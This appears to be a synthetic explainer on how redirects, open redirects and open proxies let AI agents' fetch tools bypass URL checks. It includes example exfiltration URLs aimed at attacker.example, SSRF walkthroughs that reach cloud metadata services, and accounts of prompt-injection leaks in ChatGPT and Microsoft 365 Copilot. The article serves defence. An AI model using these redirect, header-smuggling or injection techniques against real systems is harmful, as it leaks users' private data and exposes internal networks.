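# Redirects, Short Links and URL Parsing Gaps in the Fetch Tools of AI Agents

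## What does a fetch tool check before it opens a URL?

An AI agent is a program in which a language model picks the next action, such as searching a company's files or opening a web page, and ordinary software carries it out. Many agents have a fetch tool, a function that requests a URL (uniform resource locator, or web address) chosen by the model and returns the content for the model to read. Because text written by strangers may influence which URL the model chooses, developers often put a URL check in front of the tool. Before any request goes out, this code decides whether the agent may open the URL.

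A request can still end at an address the tool never approved. Websites can redirect requests to other sites, link shorteners hide one address behind another, and two programs can parse the same URL differently. Web application developers struggled with these problems long before language models could browse.

### The parts of a URL

Berners-Lee (2005), in *Uniform Resource Identifier (URI)*, laid down the general syntax of web addresses as an internet standard. An address with every part present looks like this:

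`https://anna:pw@docs.example:8443/guides/setup?lang=en#install`

| Part | In the example | Does the client send it to the server? | Does it usually end up in the server's log? |
|---|---|---|---|
| Scheme | `https` | No, it selects the protocol | No |
| User information | `anna:pw` | Many clients send it as a login | The user name, sometimes |
| Host | `docs.example` | Yes, after looking up its network address | Sometimes |
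| Port | `8443` | It selects a service on the machine; each scheme has a default | Rarely |
| Path | `/guides/setup` | Yes | Yes |
| Query | `lang=en` | Yes | Yes |
| Fragment | `install` | No | No |

The "client" here is whatever program makes the request: a browser, or the networking library inside a fetch tool.

The user information in a URL is a login placed between the double slash and the "@" sign. In `https://docs.example@attacker.example/`, the host is therefore attacker.example, and docs.example is a made-up user name. Berners-Lee warned in 2005 that someone could craft this part to look like a trusted domain, and advised programs that display URLs to make it visually distinct. The URL Standard of WHATWG, the body that maintains the rules browsers follow, treats a login in a URL as an error, but not one that makes parsing fail. A program that follows the standard may therefore record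 the error and continue parsing.

The client removes the fragment, the part of a URL that points to a place within a document, before sending the request. A secret in the fragment is therefore not sent when the fetch tool is a plain networking library, but if the tool drives a full browser, scripts on the loaded page can read the fragment and send it anywhere.

The host name in a URL can also carry data. To connect to `4471.attacker.example`, a client first asks the domain name system (DNS), the internet's directory of host names, for the matching network address. The query goes to a name server that the owner of attacker.example controls, and that server can record the full name, including the number, before the client opens a connection. A check that looks up the address before comparing the name with a list of approved sites therefore leaks the number even if it then rejects the URL.

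Data in a URL usually travels in the query, because websites use it to carry search terms, page numbers and identifiers, and it has plenty of room. Reschke, Snell and Bishop (2026) note in *The HTTP QUERY Method* that the HTTP standard recommends support for request addresses of at least 8,000 bytes, enough for roughly a thousand English words. They proposed a new kind of request partly because servers and the machines in between are more likely to log an address than the body of a request. Addresses also turn up in bookmarks.

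HTTPS does not stop an attacker from reading a secret in a URL sent to the attacker's own server. *Never Send Sensitive Information in the URL, Even Over HTTPS* (Miessler, 2015) explains that HTTPS encrypts the whole address in transit, but the receiving server decrypts it and may well log it.

### One request, one lost booking code

Suppose an assistant is helping a customer with a trip. Its context, the text given to the model, includes the customer's booking code, 4471. The assistant is allowed to open docs.example, the travel company's help site, where visitors can leave comments.

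1. The customer asks about baggage rules, and the assistant opens a page on docs.example.
2. A stranger has left a comment on that page with an instruction aimed at AI assistants. It directs them to request an address on attacker.example and to put the customer's booking code in the query.
3. The model treats the comment as part of its job and passes `https://attacker.example/log?code=4471` to the fetch tool.
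4. If no check intervenes, the tool looks up attacker.example, connects and sends a request that begins:

```
GET /log?code=4471 HTTP/1.1
Host: attacker.example
```

5. The attacker's server writes the request line to its log, and the attacker reads the code there.

The comment is a prompt injection, which hides instructions in content the model reads. The model may follow them as if the user had given them. Leaking the code is exfiltration, which means sending private data to someone who should not have it.

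The attack succeeds at step 4, and nothing later can undo it. The server may reply with a blank page, an error or an ordinary article about baggage. A filter that scans the reply for malicious content runs too late to stop the attack, and a model that notices something wrong when it reads the reply is also too late.

The HTTP standards class GET, the ordinary request for a page, as "safe". Reschke and colleagues use the term to mean that the client does not ask for any change to the state of the resource on the server, and it does not cover confidentiality. Because a fetch looks like reading, a developer could easily take "safe" to mean that an agent may fetch pages freely while needing permission to send an email. In the running example, though, the fetch tool can send a short message to a stranger.

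*Exploiting Web Search Tools of AI Agents for Data Exfiltration* (2025) demonstrates this attack end to end. The test used an agent with access to confidential company data, a blog post with an injection hidden in an extract from Wikipedia's article on artificial intelligence, and a server that logged every incoming request. When a user asked for a summary of the post, the agent retrieved the company data and sent it to the server through the same web search tool it had used to read the post. The attack needed no mail or upload function, which matters when deciding which tools to give an agent.

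*The Framing Gap* (2026) traces the risk of leaks to three ingredients in one agent: a confidential value in the context, untrusted content, and tools that act on the outside world. A language model has no built-in separation between instructions and data, so it can read text from a web page as a command. In the paper's experiments, the leak rate fell from 31.9% to zero when the agent's policy forbade disclosure of the secret "in any form", but was 48.8% when the policy named specific behaviours and omitted that phrase. A separate injection detector flagged every variant in the study without a false alarm. A prompt rule that depends so much on one clause is unreliable on its own, which is a good reason to have a check in ordinary code, where the wording of the injection doesn't affect the verdict.

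A URL check only helps if every request passes through it, and agents can cause requests without using the fetch tool. OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) lists embedded images and link previews among the requests that can happen in the background, where the user may never notice them. A chat window that displays images will load one from any address the model writes into its answer. In Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper*, a security blogger recalls reporting a leak of this type, which needed no click from the user, to OpenAI in early 2023. Microsoft's Bing Chat had the same flaw until that May, when Microsoft added a header that generally stopped images from loading. OpenAI added its first URL check in December 2023, but the blogger later found places without it, including the macOS and iOS apps.

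Willison (2024) described how a chatbot compromised by prompt injection could post a link in a workplace chat such as Slack, which then fetches the URL to show a preview and sends any data in the URL to the linked server. Because Slack makes the request, checks inside the agent's fetch tool never run. Programs that post to Slack can turn off previews for individual messages.

### Two harms

The harm in the running example is exfiltration. The other harm is that the fetch tool reaches a machine that outsiders cannot. The tool may run on a company's server or the user's laptop, and from there it can often connect to internal wikis, databases and administration pages that accept any visitor because only insiders are supposed to reach them. An injected instruction could direct the agent to `http://10.0.0.5/admin`, an address that works only inside the private network. This is server-side request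 forgery (SSRF), in which an attacker makes a server send a request of the attacker's choosing, often to machines that only that server can reach. SSRF is an old problem in web applications, and attackers can now also carry it out through language models.

In exfiltration, the URL itself carries private data to the attacker, who doesn't need the reply. A request to an internal machine may contain nothing private; the attacker wants the reply, or wants the request to do something, such as restart a service. A check that guards against one harm can therefore miss the other. `http://10.0.0.5/admin` would pass a scan for secrets, and `https://attacker.example/log?code=4471` would pass a check that only blocks internal addresses, because it leads to a public web server.

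The harms can also combine, because an internal machine's reply enters the model's context, and a later request can then leak it like any other private data there.

### The kinds of check

A host allowlist is a list of hosts that the agent may contact; the tool refuses all others or refers them to the user. With only docs.example on the list, the requests to attacker.example and 10.0.0.5 fail. The list normally allows every path and query on an approved host, so `https://docs.example/search?q=4471` passes. Whether that matters depends on who can read docs.example's logs.

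A block on private network addresses lets the agent reach any host on the public internet. The tool looks up the host's network address and refuses to connect if it is in a range that internal machines use (such as those beginning with 10, or 127.0.0.1, which a machine uses to refer to itself). This guards against SSRF but doesn't protect the booking code, because attacker.example has a public address.

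An exact-address match compares the whole URL, including its path and query, with a set of addresses that the developer has reason to consider harmless. OpenAI's version automatically fetches only addresses that an independent crawler has already seen on the public web. The crawler is unlikely to have seen an address that has just had a customer's booking code inserted into it. According to Embrace The Red, ChatGPT also accepts any address the user typed into the conversation, though the blogger presents this as a personal understanding.

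Some agents show the user the URL and ask for approval before fetching it. *Takedown* (2025), a security analysis of coding agents, examined their fetch tools and found one agent that did not ask for approval before using its built-in tool. That agent's context included the contents of the user's open files by default, so a prompt injection alone could send those out. By combining this with other flaws that allowed file reads through the agent, an attacker could get any file on the user's system.

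Developers combine these approaches. When an address fails OpenAI's match, the agent either gets an instruction to try another site or warns the user that the link may share conversation data. Frequent warnings teach people to click through without reading, which makes approval a much weaker safeguard. OpenAI also gives this as a reason against strict lists of trusted sites.

The automatic checks all assume that the tool will request the same address they examined. User approval relies on the same assumption, because the person can judge only the address on the screen. Suppose the model passes a URL *u* to the tool, which then sends requests *r*₁ to *r*ₙ. The user is protected if the check would have approved every one of these requests, not just *u*. Approval of *u* is enough if the tool sends a single request, the program that sends it interprets *u* exactly as the check did, and the host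 name still leads to the same machine as when the check ran.

In the simplest case, the check reads the host as docs.example, the tool connects to docs.example, and a page comes back. The check refuses attacker.example by name, so an attacker who wants the booking code needs a URL whose host the check reads as docs.example but that still leads the request, including the code, to attacker.example.

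## How does a redirect get past the check?

A redirect can get past the check even when the original URL looks ordinary. The check finds an approved host in `https://docs.example/old?code=4471` and allows the request. The server at docs.example responds with a redirect to attacker.example, and the networking library inside the fetch tool automatically requests the new address. The check runs only once, before the first request, so it never examines the new address.

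Websites routinely use redirects to move visitors from http to https, to keep old links working after a reorganisation, and to show a receipt after someone submits a form. Browsers and many HTTP libraries follow them automatically.

### Status codes and the Location header

Every HTTP reply begins with a three-digit status code, such as 200 for success or 404 for a missing page. A code that begins with 3 means that the client has to do something more to get what it asked for. Fielding, Nottingham and Reschke (2022), in *3xx Redirection*, a chapter of the HTTP standard, define five codes that send a client to another address. The new address stands in the Location header, one of the labelled lines at the top of the reply:

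```
HTTP/1.1 302 Found
Location: https://attacker.example/new?code=4471
```

The five codes differ in what happens to the request's method and body. The method is the kind of request, such as GET or POST, and the body holds the data that a POST request submits.

| Code | Name | Typical use | Method after a POST | Does the client resend the body? |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| 301 | Moved Permanently | A lasting move | Usually GET | No, if the method changes |
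| 302 | Found | A temporary move | Usually GET | No, if the method changes |
| 303 | See Other | A page that answers indirectly, such as a receipt | GET | No |
| 307 | Temporary Redirect | A temporary move | POST | Yes |
| 308 | Permanent Redirect | A lasting move | POST | Yes |

Codes 301 and 302 originally kept the request method, but early browsers disagreed about whether to repeat a POST at the new address, and practice settled on GET. The standard now allows this, and its editors added 307 and 308 for sites that need the method to stay the same. In *HTTP redirects* (daniel.haxx.se, 2016), Daniel Stenberg, who wrote the download tool curl, gives a table in which 301, 302 and 303 switch to GET, while 307 and 308 keep the original method. He warns that older clients may mishandle 308, which dates only from 2014. For a fetch tool that sends only GET requests, all five codes have the same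 effect.

The HTTP standard allows but does not require a client to follow redirects automatically, so a tool that stops at the first reply still complies. The standard also allows a client to follow a Location header sent with a 3xx code it doesn't recognise. A filter that checks only for 301 and 302 and leaves other codes to the library is therefore incomplete.

A Location header may give only part of an address, and the client fills in the rest from the address it just requested. For example, `Location: /guides/setup` in a reply from docs.example leads to `https://docs.example/guides/setup`. But `Location: //attacker.example/new`, which also begins with a slash, supplies a new host and keeps only the scheme. A tool that treats every redirect with a leading slash as same-site will send its next request to attacker.example. The tool has to build the full address before checking it.

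Pages can also forward a visitor without any 3xx code. http.dev's *HTTP Redirections* describes a `meta` element in the HTML that gives a delay in seconds and an address, and a script that sets the page's `window.location`. A Refresh header can do the same. http.dev notes that no HTTP standard defined this header, although all major browsers have supported it for decades. A plain networking library ignores all three methods and returns the text of a normal reply with code 200. A fetch tool that drives a full browser will load the new address, even if redirects are switched off in a library. Its developer has to intercept every page load in the browser.

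In a plain tool, the model may still read the new address in the page's markup and request it. That request is a new call to the fetch tool, so the URL check runs on it as usual.

### A naive fetch tool, line by line

Here is a short fetch tool in Python with a host allowlist. It uses Requests, a popular library for sending HTTP requests.

```python
APPROVED = {"docs.example"}

def fetch(url):
    host = urlsplit(url).hostname
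    if host not in APPROVED:
        return "refused"
    reply = requests.get(url, timeout=10)
    return reply.text
```

Suppose an injected comment has persuaded the model to pass in `https://docs.example/old?code=4471`, and docs.example redirects its `/old` page to attacker.example.

1. `urlsplit` takes the URL apart and returns the host, docs.example.
2. The comparison finds docs.example on the list, so the function carries on.
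3. `requests.get` connects to docs.example and sends `GET /old?code=4471`.
4. The reply is the 302 shown above. `requests.get` does not return yet. It reads the Location header, looks up attacker.example, connects and sends `GET /new?code=4471`.
5. The attacker's server logs the request line and sends back a page. Only now does `requests.get` return, and the function hands the page to the model as if it came from docs.example.

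The source code calls `requests.get` once, so a reviewer could reasonably expect one request. When the URL redirects, the tool sends a second request, which the check has not approved.

Requests stores the final address in `reply.url` and the earlier replies in `reply.history`, so a developer could add a line that compares the final address with the list. But that line would run after step 5, when the attacker already has the code. For JavaScript, MDN's *Response*, part of Mozilla's documentation for web developers, recommends filtering redirects when making the request, because a forged redirect can break a page that inspects the reply afterwards. The case for filtering early is much stronger for a fetch tool that holds private data.

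Several common libraries follow redirects by default, as in step 4. According to Requests' *Quickstart*, the library does so for every method except HEAD, which asks only for a page's headers, unless the developer passes `allow_redirects=False`. Go's standard HTTP client follows up to ten redirects. JavaScript's built-in `fetch` function also follows them. Deno's *property Request.redirect* gives this as the default in Deno, which runs JavaScript outside the browser, and MDN's *Request* lists the two other settings, `error` and `manual`.

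HTTPX, a newer Python library that otherwise resembles Requests, does not follow redirects unless the developer turns this on. Its *Requests Compatibility Guide* explains that automatic redirects can easily hide unnecessary network calls. The maintainers' discussion, *Reconsidering auto-redirects*, mentions that curl doesn't follow redirects by default either. Their argument was about developers not noticing extra requests, but it also applies to a URL check that doesn't cover those requests. A tool can gain or lose this protection when someone swaps one library for the other, even if the check stays the same.

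### What the last host learns

The booking code reaches attacker.example only if docs.example includes it in the Location header. The client uses the header's value as it stands and does not carry over the query from the old address.

| How docs.example chooses the target | Location header | Request line in the attacker's log |
|---|---|---|
| The target is fixed | `https://attacker.example/new` | `GET /new` |
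| It copies the query of the first address | `https://attacker.example/new?code=4471` | `GET /new?code=4471` |
| Its own code computes the target | `https://attacker.example/new/NDQ3MQ` | `GET /new/NDQ3MQ` |

With a fixed target, the attacker learns that a request arrived, when, and from which network address. Sites that copy the query usually do so after moving to a new domain, so that old links keep their search terms and page numbers. In the last row, a program on docs.example reads the request and can redirect it to any address. Here it has encoded the code in base64, a standard way of writing data as letters and digits, so a filter that searches each new address for "4471" would find nothing. An open redirect, a page that forwards visitors to any address named in the link, also belongs in this row.

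If the first URL contains nothing private, no server in the redirect chain can add the booking code to a later URL, because none of them has received it. An exact-address match therefore protects better than a host allowlist, even in a tool that follows redirects without checking them, because it rejects any first URL that contains the code.

An attacker who runs the first server doesn't need a redirect to steal data, because the first request already delivers it. To steal data past a host allowlist, the attacker needs a redirect from a host on the list. Reaching an internal machine is much easier when the check only blocks private addresses. The attacker sets up a public web server, the check approves it because its address is public, and the server redirects the tool to `http://10.0.0.5/admin`. The tool fetches that page from inside the network and brings back the reply.

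A redirect to a fixed target can also leak data through the Referer header, which contains the address the client came from. Go's client builds this header from the whole previous address, including the query, and omits it when a redirect goes from https to http. A tool built on that client could therefore send `code=4471` to attacker.example even though the Location header doesn't contain it. Fielding and colleagues list Referer among the headers that a client should remove or update before following a redirect.

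A redirect can also send other headers to the new host. Go forwards every header the calling program set, except a short list of sensitive ones such as Authorization and Cookie, which it drops when the redirect leaves the original domain and its subdomains. Many services expect their access key in a custom header that isn't on this list, so Go forwards the key. If the tool sends a POST request, a 307 or 308 makes it send the entire body again to the new host. With a browser-driven tool, the URL fragment can leak too, because the browser adds it to the new address when the Location header has no fragment.

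An attacker can spell out a secret with fixed redirects. Suppose approved hosts have ten of them, one for each digit, and each leads to a different path on attacker.example. An injected instruction could tell the agent to open the redirect for each digit of a four-digit code, in order. If the code were 4471, the attacker's log would record 4, 4, 7, 1. None of the four URLs contains the code, so a scan for secrets would pass them all.

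### Three products that checked only the first address

Researchers have found this fault in products from Microsoft and OpenAI and in a widely available open-source project. In all three cases, the attacker was a logged-in user who supplied the URL directly, without a prompt injection, and the redirect led to an internal machine rather than to a log on an outsider's server.

Copilot Studio is Microsoft's service for building custom chatbots. These chatbots can include an action that sends an HTTP request, but Microsoft blocked requests to sensitive internal addresses. In *SSRFing the Web with the Help of Copilot Studio*, researchers at the security company Tenable describe trying to reach the cloud's metadata service, an internal address where a machine can obtain its settings and access tokens. The direct request failed, as did requests with the address written as a single decimal number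 or replaced by a domain name pointing to it. The researchers then set up their own server to answer with a 301 redirect to the same address, and the error changed, showing that the request had got further.

The metadata service also checks request headers. It refuses any request that lacks the header `Metadata: true` or includes the header `X-Forwarded-For`, which Copilot Studio added by default. Tenable's researchers could set the `Metadata` header themselves. By putting extra line breaks into its value, they pushed `X-Forwarded-For` into the request body, where the service ignored it. They obtained an access token and used it to find the keys to an internal database, which let them read from and write to it. Customers shared this infrastructure. Tenable saw no other customer's data but did not know how far the write access could have reached.

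Tenable reported the flaw to Microsoft on 21 June 2024, according to its *Microsoft Copilot Studio SSRF* (2024). Microsoft confirmed the behaviour five days later and was still rolling out fixes on 23 July. Tenable's advisory lists the flaw as CVE-2024-7790, but its longer account uses CVE-2024-38206, which GCVE's public record *CVE-2024-38206* (2024) describes as a bypass of Copilot Studio's SSRF protection. The same redirect had also worked against Azure Health Bot, Azure AI Studio and Azure ML Studio. Microsoft had patched an earlier pair of SSRF flaws in the two Azure studios before Tenable could report them. Tenable then found the redirect bypass in a separate, similar interface and reported it.

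In November 2025 Jacob Krut, a security engineer, disclosed a similar flaw in ChatGPT. Users of ChatGPT can build custom GPTs, versions of the chatbot for a particular purpose, and give them "Actions" that call outside services. The builder enters the service's address and a login header, and a test button sends a request from OpenAI's own machines. Underhill (2025), in *ChatGPT Exploited Through SSRF Flaw in Custom GPT Actions*, describes how Krut got from there to the metadata service:

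1. OpenAI accepted only https addresses, and the metadata service uses plain http. A direct request therefore failed.
2. Krut entered an https address on an outside domain that answered with a 302 redirect to the metadata service. OpenAI's servers followed it.
3. The metadata service refused the request because the `Metadata: true` header was missing.
4. The form let Krut choose the name of the login header, so he named it "Metadata" and gave it the value "true". The reply contained a valid token for Azure's management interface.

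The https rule was a weak guard against internal requests, since an internal service can use https too. But this attack would have failed if OpenAI's code had also applied the rule to the second address. It would also have failed if the code had dropped the login header when the host changed, because the metadata service accepted the request only with that header. According to SecurityWeek's *ChatGPT Vulnerability Exposed Underlying Cloud Infrastructure*, the token could have given Krut access to the Azure systems that OpenAI used. OpenAI rated the flaw high severity and patched it quickly. Krut said it was not the most severe flaw he had found.

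The third case shows the cause most clearly because the code is public. Open WebUI is an AI platform that organisations run on their own servers. GitHub's *GHSA-RH5X-H6PP-CJJ6* (2026), the advisory for the flaw CVE-2026-45401, traces it to a function named `validate_url()`, which rejects private and metadata addresses but was applied only to the first URL. The libraries that then sent the requests, Requests and aiohttp (another Python library), followed redirects by default. One affected class, `SafeWebBaseLoader`, inherited its request code from an outside package, and that code passed a timeout but no redirect setting.

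Any logged-in user could exploit this and read the reply from any HTTP service that Open WebUI's server could reach, including internal databases and monitoring pages. The advisory's demonstration doesn't need an attacker's server. It submits a link to httpbin.org, a public testing site with a page that redirects to any address given in the link, and gets back Open WebUI's own internal configuration. The easiest route was a normal chat message with a link to an image, which the server fetched before passing it to the model.

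The advisory lists five places in the code with the fault, each first found by a different person. The developers had fixed one by the time GitHub published the advisory in May 2026, and the other four remained open until version 0.9.5. Rapid7, a security company, lists the flaw with a severity score of 8.5 out of 10. An earlier fix, for CVE-2025-65958, did not address redirects. A project that fetches URLs in five places has to get the same detail right in each, so it is safer to have one function that does all the fetching and that the rest of the program calls.

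### Checking every hop

The repair is to take the redirects away from the library. The tool makes each request itself, and before each one it runs the same check that it ran on the first URL. In pseudocode, for a tool that only sends GET requests:

```
function fetch(url, credentials):
    previous = none
    repeat at most 6 times:
        target = parse(url)
        if not approved(target):
            stop and report target
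        if previous exists and origin(target) != origin(previous):
            credentials = none
        reply = send GET to target with credentials,
                automatic redirects off
        if reply is not a redirect with a Location header:
            return reply
        previous = target
        url = resolve(reply.Location, relative to target)
    stop and report "too many redirects"
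```

An origin is the combination of scheme, host and port. In the running example, the first pass approves docs.example and receives the 302. The second pass parses `https://attacker.example/new?code=4471`, finds that the host isn't on the list and stops before connecting. Krut's redirect and the one in Open WebUI pointed to internal addresses, which the second pass would also have refused.

Six requests allow for five redirects, the maximum that an early version of the HTTP standard recommended. Go allows ten, and a Ruby library also named HTTPX but unrelated to the Python one allows three, according to HTTPX's *Follow Redirects*. By default, the Ruby library also refuses to follow a redirect from https to http, which would have blocked Krut's route. The limit exists to stop two pages from redirecting to each other forever. A low limit doesn't prevent an attack, because an attack needs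 only one redirect.

The credentials are whatever the tool adds to prove its identity, such as an access key or a cookie. Once the pseudocode has dropped them, they stay dropped for the rest of the chain, even if a later redirect stays on the same host. Go's HTTP client had a bug here, CVE-2024-45336. It correctly removed the Authorization header when a.tld redirected to b.tld, but put it back if b.tld then redirected to another page on b.tld, because those two addresses had the same host. Any site that received a redirect could therefore collect the key by redirecting again to one of its own pages. Go's later patch for CVE-2025-4673 made the client strip proxy credentials too.

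Comparing origins is stricter than Go's rule. Go's HTTP client keeps the Authorization header on a redirect from foo.com to sub.foo.com, and also when the same host switches from https to http, where anyone on the network path can read it. Comments in Go's source code describe this as permissive by modern standards. Companies sometimes let customers run their own pages on subdomains, where a customer could read the header, so the stricter rule is worth the occasional failed login.

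Some libraries make the loop easy to write. Go lets the developer supply a function, `CheckRedirect`, that runs before each redirect and receives the upcoming request. If the function returns an error, the client doesn't send that request. Requests and HTTPX can each return the next request without sending it, and Pydantic's *Requests Compatibility Guide* includes a short loop for both that follows a redirect chain this way. The loop isn't meant to check requests, so a developer who copies it into a fetch tool has to add a check.

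A tool that can send POST requests should also ask the user before following a 307 or 308 redirect to a different origin, because following it sends the whole request body to a new recipient.

In a simpler design, the tool doesn't follow redirects. It reports the redirect and the new address, and the model decides whether to request it. That request is a new tool call, so the check runs without any special code. Go supports this directly. If a `CheckRedirect` function returns `ErrUseLastResponse`, the client returns the redirect response instead of following it. The drawback is that the model has to take an extra step for each harmless redirect, and these are common. GitHub, for example, redirects every http address to https. A reasonable compromise is to follow redirects within one origin, checking each one, and to report the rest. When the user has to approve the new address, the tool should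 show all of it, because the query may contain the booking code.

Neither design can undo the first request. By the time the loop blocks attacker.example, docs.example has already received `GET /old?code=4471` and probably logged it. This does little harm if the log is private and the site's operator is honest. But if the check only blocks private addresses, the first host may belong to the attacker, in which case the loop protects the internal network but not the code.

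The second pass can also leak the code, because a DNS lookup alone can carry it. If docs.example computes the target `https://4471.attacker.example/`, `approved` has to compare the name with the list before looking up the network address to prevent this. A tool that may visit any public site has no such list, so it has to do the lookup.

The loop also has every weakness of the check it repeats. If the library reads an address differently from `parse`, or if a host name's network address changes between the check and the connection (DNS rebinding), the check can fail on any hop, including the first. The loop can also check only the requests that the tool itself sends. If the docs.example server fetches a page from attacker.example and returns the text, the tool receives an ordinary 200 response with no Location header to check.

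## How can an approved site lead to an unapproved one?

An approved site can pass private data to an outsider through an open redirect, an open proxy or a shared host, and checking every hop stops only the open redirect. Suppose docs.example is on the allowlist, and an injected comment persuades the model to open one of these addresses:

| Weak point on docs.example | Address the model opens | Who contacts the outsider? |
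|---|---|---|
| Open redirect | `https://docs.example/out?to=https://attacker.example/log?code=4471` | The fetch tool, after a redirect |
| Open proxy | `https://docs.example/preview?url=https://attacker.example/log?code=4471` | The docs.example server |
| Shared host | `https://docs.example/mallory/notes?code=4471` | Nobody; the outsider reads a record on docs.example |

All three addresses are on docs.example, so a host allowlist approves them. An open proxy fetches any address a visitor supplies and returns the result itself, so the tool gets an ordinary reply with no redirect to check. On a shared host, outsiders control some pages or can read how often people visit them. In this example, a user called mallory runs a page on docs.example and finds the code in that page's visitor log.

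### Open redirects

ChatGPT checked the links and images in its answers with a feature called url_safe. Before displaying one, ChatGPT sent its URL to an OpenAI server, which classed it as safe or unsafe. ChatGPT left out the unsafe ones. Tenable's *HackedGPT* concludes from tests that the result depended on the domain, the URL's parameters and the conversation so far.

Addresses on bing.com always passed the approval check. Bing's search results link to each website through an address beginning `bing.com/ck/a`, which redirects the visitor to the website. Any site in Bing's index therefore has a bing.com address that leads to it, including a site an attacker has built for the purpose.

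The check approved a bing.com address. When ChatGPT displayed the image, the request went to Bing, which redirected it to the attacker's server. OpenAI's server had checked the URL but did not load the image, so it never received the redirect.

Tenable's *OpenAI ChatGPT url_safe Mechanism Bypass* calls the tracking links essentially "an open redirect as a service". They are more limited than the open redirect in the table above, because each one leads to a single page and nobody can add a booking code to it. The researchers worked around this limit by having Bing index one page for each letter of the alphabet. To send "Hello", ChatGPT displayed the links for H, E, L, L and O in turn.

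This attack uses the spelling trick from the digit example against a real product. Choosing one of *n* links conveys at most log₂ *n* bits, so a set of 26 links conveys about 4.7 bits per request. Three requests are enough for any four-digit code, because they allow 26³ = 17,576 combinations and there are only 10,000 codes. A ten-page document would take tens of thousands of requests. The channel therefore suits short items such as passwords, codes and names, and a modest limit on requests per answer would not protect those.

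The redirect was only one part of the attack. ChatGPT left web browsing to a separate model, SearchGPT, which had no access to the user's memories or earlier chats. An injection on a web page reached only SearchGPT, so the researchers made SearchGPT end its summary with further instructions. ChatGPT read these as part of its own conversation when the user sent the next message. ChatGPT had access to the private data and displayed the images.

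Tenable reported the bypass to OpenAI on 10 December 2024, and its last recorded request for an update was on 4 March 2025. The flaw was still open when the advisory came out. In November 2025 the researchers confirmed that several of their demonstrations still worked with GPT-5. The only recorded change to the check is that OpenAI "improved the behavior of safe_url", according to Tenable's advisory for another flaw, *OpenAI ChatGPT Prompt Injection via ?q= Parameter in Web Interface*. It is unclear whether bing.com lost its standing approval.

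An open redirect can also deliver an attack, not only carry data out. *Three Vulnerabilities, One Click* (Luz, 2026) describes a chain of flaws in Anthropic's Claude that the security company Oasis named "Claudy Day". `claude.com/redirect/` forwarded visitors to any address appended to it, without validation. This defeated a Google Ads check that requires the address displayed in an advertisement to have the same host as the link behind it. An attacker could buy an advertisement that displayed claude.com and looked just like the real search result for Claude. Clicking it opened a chat on claude.ai with a prompt already in the text box, and HTML tags hid part of that prompt from the user.

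The redirect happened in the victim's browser before the agent did anything, so no URL check on a fetch tool could have stopped it. It carried no private data. The private data left later, through an upload to Anthropic's own servers. Anthropic fixed the concealed prompt but was still working on the other issues, including the redirect, when Oasis last updated its summary, *Claudy Day* (Luz, 2026), on 27 May 2026.

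### Why sites keep redirectors

Search engines send clicks on results through an address of their own first, because a direct link to another website would not let them log which result the visitor chose. Newsletters and advertisers count clicks in the same way.

Login pages need redirectors too. A visitor who opens a private page without logging in goes to the login page, and the link usually includes the private page's address so that the site can return the visitor there afterwards. If the login page doesn't check that the return address belongs to the site, it is an open redirect. Companies that move to a new domain also forward old addresses. If the forwarding page takes its target from the link without checking it, anyone can write a link that forwards to a site they choose.

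The usual fix is to keep the list of redirect targets on the server, so that a link can only select one of them. Bing's tracking links work roughly this way, but they still failed to block unapproved sites because Bing fills its list from the open web, where anyone can publish a page and wait for Bing to index it.

Some vendors don't count an open redirect by itself as a security flaw, and their bug bounty programmes pay for one only if the finder shows some further harm. This is reasonable for human visitors, because the redirect exposes nothing on the vendor's own site, an attacker could have sent a direct link instead, and the browser's address bar shows visitors where they have ended up. But the argument relies on a person who reads the address bar and can still turn back, and no one is watching when a fetch tool follows the redirect. A developer who approves a large site should therefore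 assume that it has redirectors and that its owner has no plans to remove them.

### Open proxies

Microsoft 365 Copilot answers questions from an employee's mail, files and chats. Its web page uses a Content Security Policy, a header that lists the hosts from which the browser may load images and other material. The browser also checks redirects against this list, so if an image address on an approved host redirects to attacker.example, the browser blocks the second request. To get data out, an attacker needs an approved host that makes the outside request itself, and researchers have found such hosts twice.

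Ravia (2025), in *Breaking down ‘EchoLeak’, the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability Enabling Data Exfiltration*, sets out how Aim Labs, a security research group, found the first (CVE-2025-32711):

1. An outsider sends an employee an email with instructions that appear to address the employee. Microsoft's filter for prompt injections lets it through.
2. The employee later asks Copilot an ordinary work question. The email poses as a long guide to common office topics, so Copilot is likely to retrieve it along with the material it needs.
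3. Following the instructions, Copilot writes an image into its answer, with private data from its context in the image's address. Copilot normally removes outside links, but it missed a variant of the link format that puts the address on a separate line.
4. The browser tries to load the image. The attacker's own server isn't on the policy's list, so the address has to point to an approved host.

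The researchers went through the list's more than two dozen entries one by one, starting with sharepoint.com, where any company can have its own site. Microsoft no longer allows site owners to run their own server code there or to pass a visitor's query on to an automated workflow, so controlling a page was not enough for an attacker to capture the data. SharePoint had a service that fetched an outside address to embed its content in a site. That service worked for the attack, but only if the victim had accepted an invitation to the attacker's site.

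A preview service on teams.microsoft.com had no such condition. Its link contained a `url` parameter, and Microsoft's server fetched any address placed there. The browser sent the request because the link pointed to an approved Microsoft host. Microsoft's server then contacted the attacker's server, and the private data arrived in the attacker's log without the employee having to click anything.

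Ravia also sets redirects aside on the grounds that a browser expecting an image won't follow them. That can't be true in general, because Tenable's images reached their targets through Bing's redirects. The security policy is a more likely obstacle.

Aim Labs reported EchoLeak in January 2025, and Willison (2025) noted on 11 June that the fix had been rolled out. Ravia reports that Microsoft confirmed the flaw had affected no customers, but does not explain what the company changed. *EchoLeak*, an academic case study by Reddy and Gujral, lists the defences that failed: the injection filter, the link removal and the image policy. Any one of them could have broken the chain had it worked, so the approved proxy was harmless only as long as at least one of them held.

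A year later the same policy failed again. Varonis' *SearchLeak* (2026) describes CVE-2026-42824, a flaw in the enterprise search page of Microsoft 365 Copilot. When the victim clicked a link to a genuine Microsoft address, Copilot carried out the text in the link's query as a prompt. It searched the victim's mailbox and put the title of an email into an image address. Microsoft's safeguard turned HTML in an answer into plain text only once the answer was complete, so the browser loaded the image while Copilot was still writing.

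The image address pointed to Bing because the policy approved every host under bing.com. Bing's search-by-image feature accepts a picture's address in a parameter named `imgurl`. Bing's server fetched that address to analyse the picture, which put the email's title in the attacker's log. In Varonis's example, the title included a security code. Microsoft rated the flaw critical and assigned its number on 4 June 2026, as The Next Web reported, and had patched it by the time Varonis published its findings on 15 June.

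The list that Ravia published in 2025 already included bing.com and its subdomains. Microsoft's changes after EchoLeak left them approved, and nobody appears to have checked in the meantime whether Bing would also fetch an address on request. Varonis now advises security teams to look for any approved host that fetches addresses supplied by users, because data could leave through it.

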